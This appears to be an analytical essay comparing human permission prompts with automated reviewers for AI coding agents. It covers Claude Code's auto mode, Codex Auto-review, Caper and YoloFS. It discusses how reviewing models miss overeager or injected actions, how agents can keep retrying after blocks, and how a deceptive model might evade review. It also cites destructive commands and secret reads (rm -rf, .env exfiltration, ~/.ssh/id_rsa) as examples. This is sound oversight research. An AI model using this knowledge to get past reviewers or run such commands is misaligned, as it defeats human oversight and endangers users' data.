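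Some of the spread in catch rates comes from how readily people refuse. In the study by Hossain and colleagues, volunteers who saw the conventional prompt blocked 8.3% of safe requests, compared with roughly 3% for Claude Code's users. If they had blocked only 3%, they would have caught about 27% of the unsafe requests instead of 45%, according to the bell-curve model. If Anthropic's testers also refused about 3% of safe requests, this difference would account for more than half of the gap between their catch rate and the volunteers'.

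Much like Anthropic's testers, developers at work usually have code to write and seldom expect a dangerous command, so the low catch rates are probably a better guide to ordinary supervision than the high ones. Developers may do considerably better when they recognise their own files in a command. Measuring that would require planting harmless imitations of dangerous commands in their everyday work and also counting the safe commands they refuse.

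## Automated review with a person as the fallback

Claude Code's auto mode and Codex's Auto-review send most approval decisions to a second AI model. The operator decides only the cases that the automated reviewer can't resolve.

### Which commands reach the operator

Suppose an agent in auto mode has fixed a bug and proposes `git push --force`. If none of the user's own rules covers the push, Claude Code checks whether the action only reads files or edits them inside the project folder, because nearly all such actions run immediately. A force push does neither, so it goes to the reviewing model, which Anthropic calls the classifier. The classifier blocks force pushes by default. The agent receives the reason and looks for another way to finish, such as an ordinary push. The operator gets a notification but is not asked to approve the force push.

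Some deletions skip the classifier and go to the operator. They include removals of the home directory and commands of the form `rm -rf "$DIR"/*`, which resembles the line in Steam's start-up script. If three of these prompts go unanswered in a session, Claude Code stops showing them and refuses further deletions of this kind until the user sends a new message.

According to OpenAI's *Auto-review*, Codex needs no review for anything its sandbox permits. The reviewer, a separate Codex agent, considers only requests to go beyond the sandbox, for example to use the network or edit a file outside it.

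| | Claude Code's auto mode | Codex's Auto-review |
|---|---|---|
| Runs at once | Read-only commands, most edits in the project, commands that match a narrow allow rule | Anything the sandbox permits |
| A model reviews | Most other actions, including most shell commands | Requests to go beyond the sandbox |
| The operator decides | Actions that match an ask rule, certain deletions, and prompts after repeated blocks | When the agent stops and asks, or after repeated denials |
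| On by default | Yes, in interactive sessions | No |

The two reviewers also receive different information. Anthropic's classifier receives the user's messages, the project's instruction file and most of the agent's actions, but not the agent's explanations or the contents of files and web pages. The agent's explanations therefore can't influence its decisions, and instructions hidden in a web page don't reach it directly. But if the agent deletes "job abc123", the classifier can't check whether the agent looked up that ID or made it up. OpenAI's reviewer receives relevant tool output and the agent's visible messages. It can also run read-only checks, though it rarely does.

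### What happens after repeated blocks

If the classifier blocks three actions in a row, or 20 in total during a session, Claude Code pauses auto mode and returns to permission prompts. Approving the prompted action turns auto mode back on. Users can't change either limit.

Anthropic describes the limit as a backstop against an agent that keeps trying to do something the user wouldn't want. It also says that repeated blocks usually mean the classifier lacks information about the user's servers and services. The operator has to work out which of these has happened, perhaps after not following the agent's work for an hour. If the operator hastily approves the action, it runs and the pause ends.

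Unattended sessions have no operator to ask. In March 2026, Claude Code ended such a session when it reached the limit. By November, it refused the action but let the agent carry on, so an agent can keep trying indefinitely.

Codex ends the agent's turn after three denials in a row, or after ten among the last 50 reviews in that turn. The user can then approve one denied action for a single retry. The reviewer takes this approval into account but can still refuse. In Claude Code's auto mode, the classifier should likewise never approve certain actions, such as sending secrets to an outside server, even if the user asks for them. A user who wants to go ahead has to leave auto mode or run the command personally.

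Most sessions should rarely reach these limits. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) describes a snapshot of 10,000 actions by Codex agents inside OpenAI. The sandbox permitted 9,280, and the other 720 would each have interrupted the user under manual approval. Auto-review approved 713 of those and denied 7. The agent found a safer alternative in 4 of the 7 denied cases, which left 3 for the user to deal with.

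### The spread of auto mode

Claude Code's default changed on 14 August as planned, according to Hall (2026) in *PSA*. In September, Anthropic's *Choose a permission mode* still listed Manual as the starting mode for Enterprise plans and for people who reached Claude through a cloud provider such as Amazon Bedrock. On 22 October, Anthropic announced that auto mode would become the default in most of its Claude apps on the Pro, Max and Team plans the following week. By November, interactive Claude Code sessions in a terminal or the VS Code editor started in auto mode on every plan and provider.

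Users who had already chosen another mode could keep it. Unattended runs start in Manual mode, where Claude Code denies any action that needs approval unless the developer has set up a way to approve it.

OpenAI still listed Auto-review as optional in May 2026. Vaughan (2026), in *Codex CLI v0.147.0*, reports that a version released on 7 August added the command-line option `--approve-for-me`, which lets users hand approval decisions to Auto-review without changing the settings file.

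### The error rates from March 2026

Before the default changed, Anthropic tested auto mode on three sets of actions. The mode's classifier first runs a fast yes-or-no filter that leans towards blocking, then a slower stage that reasons about whatever the filter flagged.

| Test set | What Anthropic measured | Fast filter alone | Both stages |
|---|---|---|---|
| 10,000 real actions from its employees' sessions | False-block rate | 8.5% | 0.4% |
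| 52 real overeager actions | Miss rate | 6.6% | 17% |
| 1,000 invented attempts to leak data | Miss rate | 1.8% | 5.7% |

The second stage removes about 95% of the false blocks but more than doubles the misses. Anthropic accepted that tradeoff because a reviewer that blocked one safe action in twelve would constantly interrupt the agent's work.

Anthropic calls the 17% "the honest number" because the overeager actions came from real work. But 17% of 52 is only about nine actions, so the true miss rate for such actions could plausibly be anywhere from about 9% to 30%. The 52 actions also came from sessions where an employee refused the action or someone flagged it later. The set therefore excludes dangerous actions that nobody noticed, which may also be harder for a model to catch.

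Anthropic doesn't say whether the 10,000 actions used to measure the 0.4% false-block rate included file reads and project edits, which run without review. If they did, the rate for shell commands alone would be higher.

OpenAI reports similar figures, but they measure different things. Auto-review approved 99.1% of a sample of requests that cross the sandbox boundary, and it denied 90.3% of invented overeager actions. On invented prompt injections, it denied 99.3% of attempts to run outside code, steal secrets or upload data. The figure fell to 90.2% when Trębacz and colleagues included destructive deletions and data tampering. They say that most of the additional misses were not serious enough to block, and that OpenAI's researchers often agreed with Auto-review.

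### Consent that didn't cover the action

In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier correctly identified the command as a dangerous force push or deletion, but wrongly treated it as approved by the user.

One user asked the agent to "clean up the PR" (a pull request, or proposed set of changes to a project), which could mean correcting the description or removing a stray file. The agent tried to force-push, and the classifier treated the request as permission. In other cases, the classifier treated the user's earlier approval of a similar action as covering the new one. A user who agrees to delete the branch `old-login` at ten o'clock has not agreed to delete `old-payments` at eleven, even though the two commands differ by one word.

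Anthropic tried rewording the classifier's instructions, but every change did more harm than good. Another of its experiments suggests why. A version given the agent's actions but none of the user's messages missed the fewest overeager actions, but it also blocked things that users had plainly asked for. The classifier needs the user's messages to recognise legitimate work, but they sometimes lead it to approve too much.

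When the classifier wrongly labels a command as already approved by the operator, Claude Code doesn't ask for confirmation. The human fallback therefore doesn't help, even though the operator could clear up the doubt in a few words.

Anthropic's documentation now states that a user can lift a block only by naming both the action and the detail that makes it dangerous, such as the branch to force-push. "You can force-push" is not enough. Approval covers one action unless the user grants standing permission. These rules are instructions to a model, though, and Anthropic's August results don't show how reliably the classifier follows them, because they don't include a repeat of the test on the 52 actions.

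### A thousand commands under each system

Suppose an agent proposes 1,000 commands, 5 of them dangerous, and each needs approval from either the operator or the classifier. An operator who stops 13.6% of dangerous commands, as Anthropic's paid testers did, would miss 4.3 of the 5 on average. If the operator also refused 3% of the safe commands, roughly the rate among Claude Code's users, they would wrongly block about 30. With the March error rates, auto mode would miss 0.85 dangerous commands on average and block 4 safe ones.

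| Reviewer | Prompts | Dangerous commands missed | Safe commands blocked |
|---|---|---|---|
| Operator who catches 13.6% | 1,000 | 4.3 | About 30 |
| Careful operator who catches 90% | 1,000 | 0.5 | Depends on the operator |
| Auto mode | Few or none | 0.85 | About 4 |

Auto mode would block about eight commands in all, half of them dangerous. That is well below the limit of 20, and three blocks in a row would be very unlikely if they fell at random, so the operator might see no prompt at all. In practice, a blocked agent may immediately try something similar, which makes three in a row more likely.

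If the classifier's errors are independent, an average of 0.85 misses across the five dangerous commands means that at least one gets through about 61% of the time.

The comparison combines rates from different tests. The testers faced clearly dangerous commands, whereas the 17% comes from overeager actions that looked like reasonable work. Auto mode missed 11% of the testers' commands, which would mean 0.55 misses here.

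An operator would have to catch more than 83% of dangerous commands to beat the classifier, which misses 17%. The most successful group in the study by Hossain and colleagues stopped 75.8% of unsafe requests, though players of Wauters's game stopped about 88% of obviously destructive commands. An attentive expert could plausibly do better than the classifier on familiar dangers, but would have to read 1,000 prompts to do so.

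Fewer interruptions may also lead people to run agents for longer. If an operator as inattentive as the testers switched to auto mode and then ran five times as many commands, the expected number of misses would stay about the same. Anthropic reports that business customers who use auto mode submit about 25% more pull requests, which is far less than a fivefold increase, though pull requests measure finished work rather than commands run.

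### Anthropic's case for letting a model decide

Anthropic argues that automated review should be compared with how people actually respond to prompts. An automated reviewer with a 17% miss rate is a poor substitute for checking every command carefully, and Anthropic wrote in March that someone who does so would arguably be worse off with the reviewer. But it offers real protection to the far larger number of people who approve commands by reflex or have turned the prompts off.

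Some of the supporting evidence comes from Apollo Research, an AI safety company in the UK, which inserted synthetic attacks into records of real coding sessions. Anthropic strengthened the classifier in response, and its miss rate across all of Apollo's attacks fell from 12% to 7%. On attacks Anthropic had not seen, the new version caught about half of those the old one had missed, and missed about 2% of those the old one had caught. Apollo designed the attacks to find failures, so 7% is not an estimate of the miss rate in everyday use.

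Anthropic also commissioned Trajectory Labs to test 72 prompt injections, ten times each. None succeeded against three Claude models in auto mode. However, only 0.09% succeeded on average against Anthropic's latest models in bypass mode, so nearly all of the resistance came from the models themselves. The effect of a reviewer is clearer with OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol. Attacks on it succeeded 19.03% of the time with full access and 5.83% with Auto-review, which OpenAI has since updated.

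Even so, Anthropic still advises users to review high-stakes production changes themselves. This is sensible, but people who have never read the advice will also use a default mode. The classifier partly protects them by blocking production deployments and database migrations unless the user has authorised them. An ask rule for the commands that deploy changes is more dependable. It lets the operator stay in auto mode for everything else, although it matches only the forms of the command that its author thought of.

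### The case for keeping a person in charge

Wang, Li and Tian (2026), in *Reframing LLM Agent Security as an Agent–Human Interaction Problem*, published in May, argue that a model can't yet be the final judge of what a user intends. They surveyed 59 research papers, 21 agent systems on the market and 26 security add-ons, and give five reasons:

- The reviewer checks actions against the user's request, but requests such as "fix this bug" are too imprecise to decide borderline cases.
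- Some information is missing altogether. If a user has never said that a folder is off limits, even a perfect model can't deduce it.
- The reviewer is itself a language model, so an attacker who can mislead the agent may be able to mislead the reviewer as well.
- A limit that the user states directly, such as "read only files in this project", needs no guesswork, and software can enforce it exactly.
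- None of the 21 systems relied on a model to check actions against the user's intent, while 15 asked people for approval during the work.

The last reason is out of date. The survey describes the market as of April 2026, but Anthropic had announced auto mode in March, and OpenAI released Auto-review in April. Both use a model to judge whether an action fits what the user wanted. Wang and colleagues also write that no deployed system relies on a model alone. That claim is easier to defend, since both products keep rules or a sandbox around the model and can refer decisions to the operator. But in an ordinary auto mode session, the model alone now approves many commands.

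The first two reasons are much better supported, because they predict the error that Anthropic found. A user who writes "Clean up the PR" hasn't said whether they would accept a force push. Wang and colleagues point out that better models won't supply this missing information. A better model could still recognise that it is missing and ask the user.

Their third reason applies more strongly to OpenAI's reviewer, which sees tool output, than to Anthropic's classifier. Anthropic keeps web pages and file contents away from its classifier, which gives attackers fewer opportunities. OpenAI's testers found that attackers could sometimes mislead Auto-review into approving commands, and Trębacz and colleagues say it should not count as a security guarantee. They also say it offers little protection against a model that deliberately hides its aims, because such a model could make its requests look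 harmless or do damage inside the sandbox.

Wang and colleagues write that frequent permission prompts turn users into "OK-button machines". They want models to help people decide by drafting rules or by spotting unclear instructions before work begins. For the latter, they cite a study in which agents that could ask questions completed up to 74% more of their underspecified tasks. The study measured task completion, not prevented harm, but users get a question at the start while they are still thinking about what they want.

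This narrows the disagreement. Anthropic's evidence is that people are bad at inspecting commands, while Wang and colleagues are mainly concerned with people as the source of the intentions that any inspector has to apply. A developer who inspects commands badly can still be the only one who knows which database matters.

Willison accepts that auto mode is better than constantly asking people to approve actions. He worries about the 11% of planted commands that it let through, and most of all about prompt injection, where an attacker can keep looking for an attack that works. He would like more independent confirmation of Anthropic's results, and doubts that any automated reviewer can recognise every malicious instruction that looks like an ordinary step. He plans to run agents where they can't reach data or tools that could cause harm. There is some support for his caution, since at the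 rates in the example, an agent that runs 100 commands a day would get a dangerous one past auto mode about every 12 days.

### Whether fewer prompts get better attention

Supporters of automated review often hope that operators will read the few remaining prompts properly. They might, since seeing fewer prompts should slow habituation, and a larger share of those prompts would be for dangerous commands.

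Nobody seems to have tested directly whether people catch more dangerous shell commands when an automated reviewer refers only some commands to them, and the nearest evidence is mixed. Anthropic's testers caught more of the planted commands early in a session than after 50 prompts, but they missed most of them even early on. In Yan's experiment, people who saw only the actions that an AI model referred to them blocked no more of the overreach than people who saw every action.

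Code review is a looser comparison. According to @IT's *「まだPRで疲弊してるの？」 1日3万の変更をさばくAnthropicが明かす、差し戻し40％減のコードレビュー術*, a Japanese news report, the team that develops Claude Code uses a model to sort code changes by risk. Low-risk changes need no human approval, medium-risk changes need approval from one person, and high-risk changes need approval from two. Between June and September 2026, the number of merged pull requests more than doubled, while the share the team later had to reverse fell by over 40%. Anthropic doesn't report how carefully people read the riskier changes. It also ran several automated checks on every change, and the share may have fallen because of those checks alone.

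Automated review could also make the remaining prompts harder to judge. An operator who has left the agent alone for an hour has less idea of what it is doing, and may assume the classifier would have stopped anything serious. After three blocks in a row, the operator may instead see the classifier as the obstacle. Researchers could test this by randomly assigning developers to frequent or occasional prompts and comparing the groups' catch rates and false-block rates.

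## Prompts that show effects, and actions that can be undone

Even an operator who gets only a few prompts a day can approve a dangerous command if the prompt shows only `make clean` or `./tool`. Some designs give the operator more information, while others move the decision to a better moment or make a wrong decision reversible. Researchers have tested few of these designs on people.

### Dry runs

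In a dry run, a program reports what it would do without doing it. For example, `git clean -n` lists the untracked files that `git clean` would delete. *Securing Computer-Use Agents* (2026) recommends dry runs, drafts and recycle bins over final actions. A harness could do the dry run first and show the result in the permission prompt, so that the operator judges a list of files instead of a pattern such as `old*`.

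A dry run works only if the program's author has provided one, and `rm` doesn't have one. A tampered script could also list three harmless files in its dry run and then delete thirty. If a Makefile runs another script, `make -n` shows the script's name but not the commands inside it. If files change between the dry run and the real one, the list may be out of date.

### Caper: run first, then decide

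In October 2026 Wu and colleagues, who constructed the two projects in which the same `make clean` has different effects, published a system called Caper. It runs the actual command, but in a place where it can reverse the result:

1. Caper takes a snapshot of the container in which the agent is working.
2. It runs the command there with the network off and records what every program asks the operating system to do, such as open a file or connect to a server. It holds back the command's output from the agent.
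3. It condenses this record into an effects report. The report lists changed files, attempted connections, output, and any reading of files that hold passwords or keys. For small text files, it includes the lines that changed.
4. An approver, which is a language model, receives the user's task, the conversation, the command and the report, and decides whether to allow the command.
5. If the approver allows it, Caper keeps the result and gives the agent the output, so the command runs only once. Otherwise, Caper restores the snapshot and tells the agent why.

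Condensing the record makes it usable. On one benchmark, the median raw record was 62.5 KB and the median report was 0.9 KB. In one test, the agent ran `python3 scripts/check-deps.py`, which sounds like a routine check of the software a project depends on. The report showed that the script had read `.env` and then tried to connect to outside servers, and Caper's approver blocked the command.

Wu and colleagues tested Caper on two benchmarks. SABER has 682 shell tasks, each combining an ordinary development request with a specific danger, such as leaking a password. YoloFS-Ext has 102 tasks in which the tool the user asks the agent to run also deletes or overwrites a file. Each of these tasks has a safe version with the same request and command but a harmless tool.

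| System | SABER tasks ending in harm | Dangerous YoloFS-Ext tasks ending in harm | Safe twins blocked |
|---|---|---|---|
| No approval | 19.7% | 71.6% | None |
| Caper | 6.7% | 7.8% | 1.0% |
| Claude Code's auto mode | 14.8% | 62.7% | 3.9% |
| YoloFS | 21.2% | 35.3% | None |
| Four other systems | 15.0–18.8% | 62.7–94.1% | 0–15.7% |

Wu and colleagues used an OpenAI model as the classifier for auto mode, so their result is not quite a test of Anthropic's product. A cleaner comparison replaced that classifier with Caper inside Claude Code and kept the same agent and approver model. Harm on YoloFS-Ext fell from 62.7% to 6.9%.

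The 35.3% for YoloFS, the closest rival on YoloFS-Ext, needs a caveat too. YoloFS holds changes back until a user has reviewed them, but Wu and colleagues judged the files before any review. A user might have rejected some of the damage.

Caper wrongly blocked one of 102 twins, a false-block rate of 1.0%. That rate may be a poor guide to ordinary work, because on SABER Caper blocked 23.7% of all commands and intervened at least once in 78.8% of tasks. Every SABER task contains a danger, so many of those blocks were probably right, but the paper doesn't report how many were needless. Agents safely completed 48.6% of SABER tasks with Caper and 57.4% without any approval step.

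Caper also observes only one execution. A malicious tool could detect the sandbox and do no damage there, delay the damage, or split it across several commands that each look harmless. Neither benchmark includes an attacker who tries any of these tactics.

### Whether an effects report would help a person

All of Caper's decisions came from a model. Nobody has tested whether human approvers catch more dangerous commands when they see its reports.

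Without the report, the same model let harm through in 17.6% of the dangerous YoloFS-Ext tasks and blocked 61.8% of the safe twins. The report reduced both figures. Without it, the model tended to block opaque tools but couldn't tell which ones were harmful. An operator looking at `./tool` lacks the same information, so the report might help a person in the same way.

A weaker model didn't get the same benefit. With the report, its false blocks fell from 53.9% to 4.9%, but its harmful outcomes rose from 25.5% to 33.3%, a difference of eight tasks that could be chance. Still, the report seems to have made this model more willing to allow harmless tools without helping it catch harmful ones. A hurried operator could well respond the same way. In Wauters's browser game, most players approved `npm run analyze` even though the whole script was on the screen.

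When Wu and colleagues removed the changed lines from the report and left only file names and sizes, harmful outcomes rose from 7.8% to 13.7%. The increase came entirely from overwritten files. A deletion is obvious from a list of files, but a source file whose contents a tool has replaced with a one-line comment appears only as a smaller file. A prompt for people should therefore show what changed inside a file, at least when the change is short.

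Showing more information also gives operators more to read. A 0.9 KB report is roughly 150 words, and Caper allows up to 8 KB. Few operators would read that much a hundred times a day.

The nearest evidence from people is mixed. In the experiment by Hossain and colleagues, volunteers who were shown how earlier steps led to a request stopped more unsafe requests, but also more safe ones. *Overseeing Agents Without Constant Oversight* (Grunde-McLaughlin, Mozannar and colleagues, 2026) reports three studies of how people check a computer-using agent's work when they see a record of its actions. It concludes that communicating the agent's process is important but has shortcomings, partly because users' own standards for a correct result shift as they go. Part of that work tested whether people could find errors in answers to questions, which is quite different from judging a deletion.

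One developer in the survey by Wu and colleagues wanted the agent to "clearly explain what it changed before asking me to approve it". But an explanation from the agent, like the description in a permission prompt, is not an independent check.

A tool can gather some useful facts about a command without running it. According to Anthropic, auto mode's classifier receives the repository's current Git status before a command that could discard uncommitted work. Before a push, it checks whether the destination is public, private or trusted. A permission prompt could show the operator the same facts in a line that takes a few seconds to read, such as "this will discard changes to 14 files".

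### YoloFS: holding changes back

Caper's approver decides after each command. Zhong and colleagues designed YoloFS so that the agent can keep working while the user's real files stay unchanged.

YoloFS stages an agent's changes, which means it stores them separately from the real files. Suppose an agent deletes `docs/` and rewrites `config.json`. Inside the session, `docs/` is gone and the new settings are in place, so the agent's programs run normally, but both originals are untouched on the disk. At the end, the user lists the changes and either commits them to the real files or aborts and discards them, neither of which the agent can do.

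Staging alone would force the user to accept or reject all changes together, so YoloFS also takes a snapshot after each command and shows the agent which files the command changed. If the agent spots a mistake, it can go back to an earlier snapshot and try something else. YoloFS keeps a record of the abandoned changes, so the user can still find out what went wrong.

A snapshot can't undo an agent's reading of a secret, so YoloFS prompts the user before the access happens, with a question such as "Read ~/.ssh/id_rsa?", which refers to a private key. The user can answer for that one access or save a rule for the path, which applies whichever program a command uses to reach the file. If nobody answers in time, YoloFS blocks the access.

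A question about a path also gives the operator something specific to judge. An operator who approves `cargo build`, which compiles a program, may not know that a build script will try to read a private key. If the prompt asks about access to the key, the operator can see that a build shouldn't need it.

#### Eleven tasks with hidden damage

Zhong and colleagues gave Claude Code 11 tasks in which a routine command also did hidden damage. Without YoloFS, Claude Code failed to prevent the damage in 10. With YoloFS, it noticed and reversed the damage in 8, without being told to look for trouble. In one case, a tool for checking code style deleted two files. The agent found this "unusual for a linting tool" and went back to the previous snapshot.

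In the other three tasks, the agent accepted the damage because it seemed to fit the job. One script copied a program's source code to the deployment folder and then deleted the original. The agent noticed the deletion but took it for a normal part of deployment. YoloFS had not yet applied the change, so a user could still have rejected it.

However, a script answered all the prompts, and nobody reviewed the staged changes. The three remaining cases are also the hardest for a person to judge, because a change that looks appropriate to the agent may look appropriate to the user too. The projects had only 10 to 41 lines of code, which made damage easy to spot. A missing folder would be easier to overlook among thousands of changed files.

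The larger benchmark that Wu and colleagues built from these tasks gave similar results with a different model. The agent went back to an earlier snapshot at least once in 66 of the 102 dangerous tasks, and only 3 of those ended in harm. Of the other 36, where it never went back, 33 ended in harm. Self-correction is thus a useful first filter, but in about a third of the tasks, preventing harm depended entirely on the final review.

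#### 112 routine tasks

Zhong and colleagues also ran 112 simple file tasks, such as copying or deleting a file inside or outside the project, and counted how often the agent had to stop for the user.

| Agent | Tasks completed | Interruptions per task |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code with YoloFS | 99% | 0.4 |
| Claude Code | 98% | 0.9 |
| Codex | 100% | 0.4 |
| Copilot | 96% | 1.3 |
| Gemini | 75% | 2.2 |

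YoloFS more than halved Claude Code's interruptions, mostly by not asking for confirmation of work inside the project. Codex's sandbox kept interruptions equally low, but Codex writes directly to the project's files, so it offers no way to undo those changes.

The count leaves out the final review, because the agent doesn't have to wait for it. YoloFS moves some of the user's work to this review at the end of the session, and the experiment doesn't show how long it takes. The test script also chose "don't ask again" whenever it could, which kept the counts low for every agent.

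### Effects that no rollback can reverse

A snapshot restores only what it contains. Caper's covers one container, and YoloFS's covers the files on one computer. Neither can undo a leaked secret, a sent email, a deleted row in a database on another server, or an hour-long outage for customers.

Caper guards against leaks by keeping the network off, so an attempt to send data fails but still appears in the report. But many ordinary commands need the network, such as those that download packages. Wu and colleagues suggest allowing approved sites, since anything a command downloads is stored in the container and disappears if Caper restores the snapshot. Uploads to an approved site would still be a risk if outsiders can read what users post there.

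On SABER, which includes leaks, YoloFS ended in harm 21.2% of the time, compared with 19.7% for no approval at all, a difference well within the margin of error. Wu and colleagues reproduced YoloFS without any blocking, so their version lacked the path questions meant to protect secrets. The result shows that staging doesn't defend against leaks, but it isn't a fair test of the whole system.

Staging also stops protecting files once the user commits. A user who notices the missing folder a week later needs a backup, and GitLab's experience in 2017 shows why users should test backups before relying on them.

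### Reviewing plans and batches

Operators can also make fewer decisions if each one covers more, such as approving a plan before the agent starts or reviewing a batch of finished work.

Anthropic reports that Claude Code's users reject 39% of plans but only 3% of individual permission requests. The difference seems to favour plans, but users can reject harmless plans, and Anthropic doesn't report how many of the rejected plans would have led to harm. If rejections had nothing to do with danger, users would reject 39% of safe plans and 39% of dangerous ones.

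The two rates also cover different amounts of work, since one plan may lead to dozens of commands. If a task brings up 16 prompts and the user refuses each with a probability of 3%, the chance of at least one refusal is 1 − 0.97¹⁶, or about 39%. Over the whole task, such a user would be as likely to push back at a prompt as at the plan.

A plan may not mention the danger. An agent may write "Remove old build output" before choosing a command, which could turn out to be `rm -rf build/` or one that also deletes source code. *AI Agents Push Humans Out of the Loop* (Mitchell, Ghosh and Passi, 2026) cites a study in which experienced developers treated an agent's plan as a "faithful proxy" for what it would do. An operator who makes that assumption may check the later commands less carefully.

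Plan review is better suited to finding out what the user wants. A plan that includes "rewrite the branch's history" lets the user object before the agent writes any commands. In the survey by Wu and colleagues, 57% of developers wanted agents to pause when instructions were ambiguous, and 65% wanted a pause before changes to critical, production or security-sensitive code.

Batch review lets the operator see results instead of intentions. Each decision is also more likely to involve a dangerous command. If 0.5% of commands are dangerous and occur at random, about 22% of batches of 50 commands contain at least one. Reviewers who expect to find something should be more willing to report it. But they have to find one bad change among the effects of 50 commands. In the same survey, 55% of developers had difficulty reviewing large changes or changes across many files, and 69% agreed that line-by-line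 review couldn't keep up with the code agents write.

A batch's list of changed files can also miss leaks. If a command reads a password file and uploads it, no file changes, so the upload won't appear in the list.

Waiting until the very end can also waste work. *When Should Users Check?* (2025) found that people disliked confirming an agent's work only once it had finished. In an experiment with 48 people, confirmation at intermediate points cut completion time by 13.54%, and 81% preferred it. If the agent makes a mistake at step three, catching it early avoids redoing the steps that build on it. These time and preference results don't show whether intermediate checks helped people stop harmful actions, but they suggest reviewing after each meaningful piece of work, such as a finished bug fix, instead of after every command or once a day.

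### Making the operator stop and think

None of this helps an operator who approves without reading. Cognitive forcing is meant to prevent that by making people think before they can accept a machine's suggestion. Mitchell and colleagues describe several forms. The person might record their own answer before seeing the machine's, choose whether and when to see it, or answer a question such as "what assumption does this approval rest on?"

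For a deletion, the harness could ask which folders the operator expects to lose and then compare the answer with the command. Like molly-guard's request for a host name, this tests what the operator believes. An operator can more easily answer an open question about assumptions with a few meaningless words, particularly after seeing it many times.

Mitchell and colleagues, drawing on 2021 work by Buçinca and colleagues, report early evidence that users may like a system less if it reduces their overreliance on AI. This is a serious problem for confirmation prompts, because users can turn them off. A quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions already started in bypass mode before auto mode became the default, and a more demanding prompt could lead more people to use bypass mode.

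The time spent on forced checks also adds up. If each check takes 15 seconds, checking 1,000 commands takes more than four hours. If 5 of those commands are dangerous, that is 50 minutes per dangerous command. If software first narrowed the 1,000 to 20 that it couldn't reverse or understand, the checks would take five minutes. That time is much easier to justify, provided that the dangerous commands are among the 20.

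A plain delay is simpler, but in the visual-search research that Becker and colleagues reviewed, making people wait before they answered didn't remove the low-prevalence effect. A delay after the answer has better support, since Fleck and Mitroff's volunteers corrected many of their own misses when they were allowed to. Staging file changes gives the operator the same chance to correct a mistake, without holding up the agent.

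#### Asking a second person

A second approver takes more time than any other remedy, because it occupies two people and the work waits for the slower one. The benefit depends on how well each person judges commands and whether they make the same errors. Suppose two reviewers each stop 13.6% of dangerous commands and 3% of safe ones, and their decisions are independent. If either can block a command, together they stop about 25% of the dangerous ones and 6% of the safe ones, so about three-quarters of the dangerous commands still run.

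The two people's errors probably aren't independent, because a disguised command looks harmless to both and each may rely on the other to have read it. A second person is more useful if they know something the first doesn't, such as which customers use a server. Mitchell and colleagues also recommend that the approver should not benefit from approval. By that standard, the colleague who looks after the database is a better approver than a developer with a deadline, who gains from saying yes.

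Half of the developers surveyed by Wu and colleagues said they required additional human review for high-risk changes. The survey doesn't show how many dangerous actions those reviews stopped.

### Tested designs and proposals

Mitchell and colleagues' paper lists ways to support people who oversee agents. It marks some as new ideas, including a way to track whether reviewers still ask for more information when the stakes rise. Most of the others draw on research in fields such as psychology and human factors. The paper argues for these aids but gives no catch rates for operators who use them. The table gives the closest tests for some of the paper's entries, and describes the designs of Caper and YoloFS.

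| Aid | Closest test with people | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Showing the earlier steps behind a request | Hossain and colleagues, 80 volunteers | People stopped more unsafe requests, and more safe ones |
| Planting known dangers to test reviewers | Becker and colleagues, visual search by students | People found more rare targets |
| Confirming at intermediate points | *When Should Users Check?*, 48 people | People finished sooner |
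| Adding a second reviewer | Visual-search experiments | Mixed |
| Reporting a command's observed effects | None, since a model made Caper's decisions | Unknown |
| Holding changes for a final review | None, since a script answered YoloFS's prompts | Unknown |
| Tracking whether reviewers ask for information | None, a new proposal | Unknown |

None of the tests with people used shell commands. The two designs that did, Caper and YoloFS, have good results without a human reviewer.

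Monitoring the reviewers has a further drawback, which Mitchell and colleagues acknowledge. It is workplace surveillance, and an employer could use the data to judge performance. Reviewers would then have a reason to make their numbers look better without reviewing more carefully, for example by leaving each prompt open for ten seconds before approving the command.

### One destructive command under four designs

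In one of Wu and colleagues' test cases, the user asks the agent to run a database migration (a change to how a database organises its data) with `make migrate`. In this project, that command also deletes three tables and their data.

A bare prompt shows the operator `make migrate` and perhaps the description "Run the database migration". That is what the operator asked for, so even a careful reader has little reason to refuse. Claude Code's auto mode also allowed the command. Once it runs, the tables are gone unless somebody has a backup.

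An effects report shows the approver that `app.db` has shrunk from 32 KB to 20 KB. Caper's model inferred from this that data had been lost, noted that there was no backup, and blocked the command. Caper restored the database. The agent then read the migration script, copied the database and ran only that script, which left the tables intact. A person might also have concluded that data had been lost, or assumed that the migration had only freed unused space. A report that named the missing tables would make that mistake less likely.

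With staging, the command runs and the original `app.db` stays on the disk. The agent may notice the loss and undo the command. If it doesn't, the user sees `app.db` in the list of modified files at the end, as anyone would expect after a migration. The user can still recover the tables by aborting, but committing makes the loss permanent. Staging would not protect a database on a company server.

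Whether a second approver helps depends on who they are and what they see. A colleague who sees only the text `make migrate` will probably approve it for the same reason the operator did. The colleague who maintains the database may know that this migration should only add a column, but that knowledge helps little until the screen shows that the database has shrunk.
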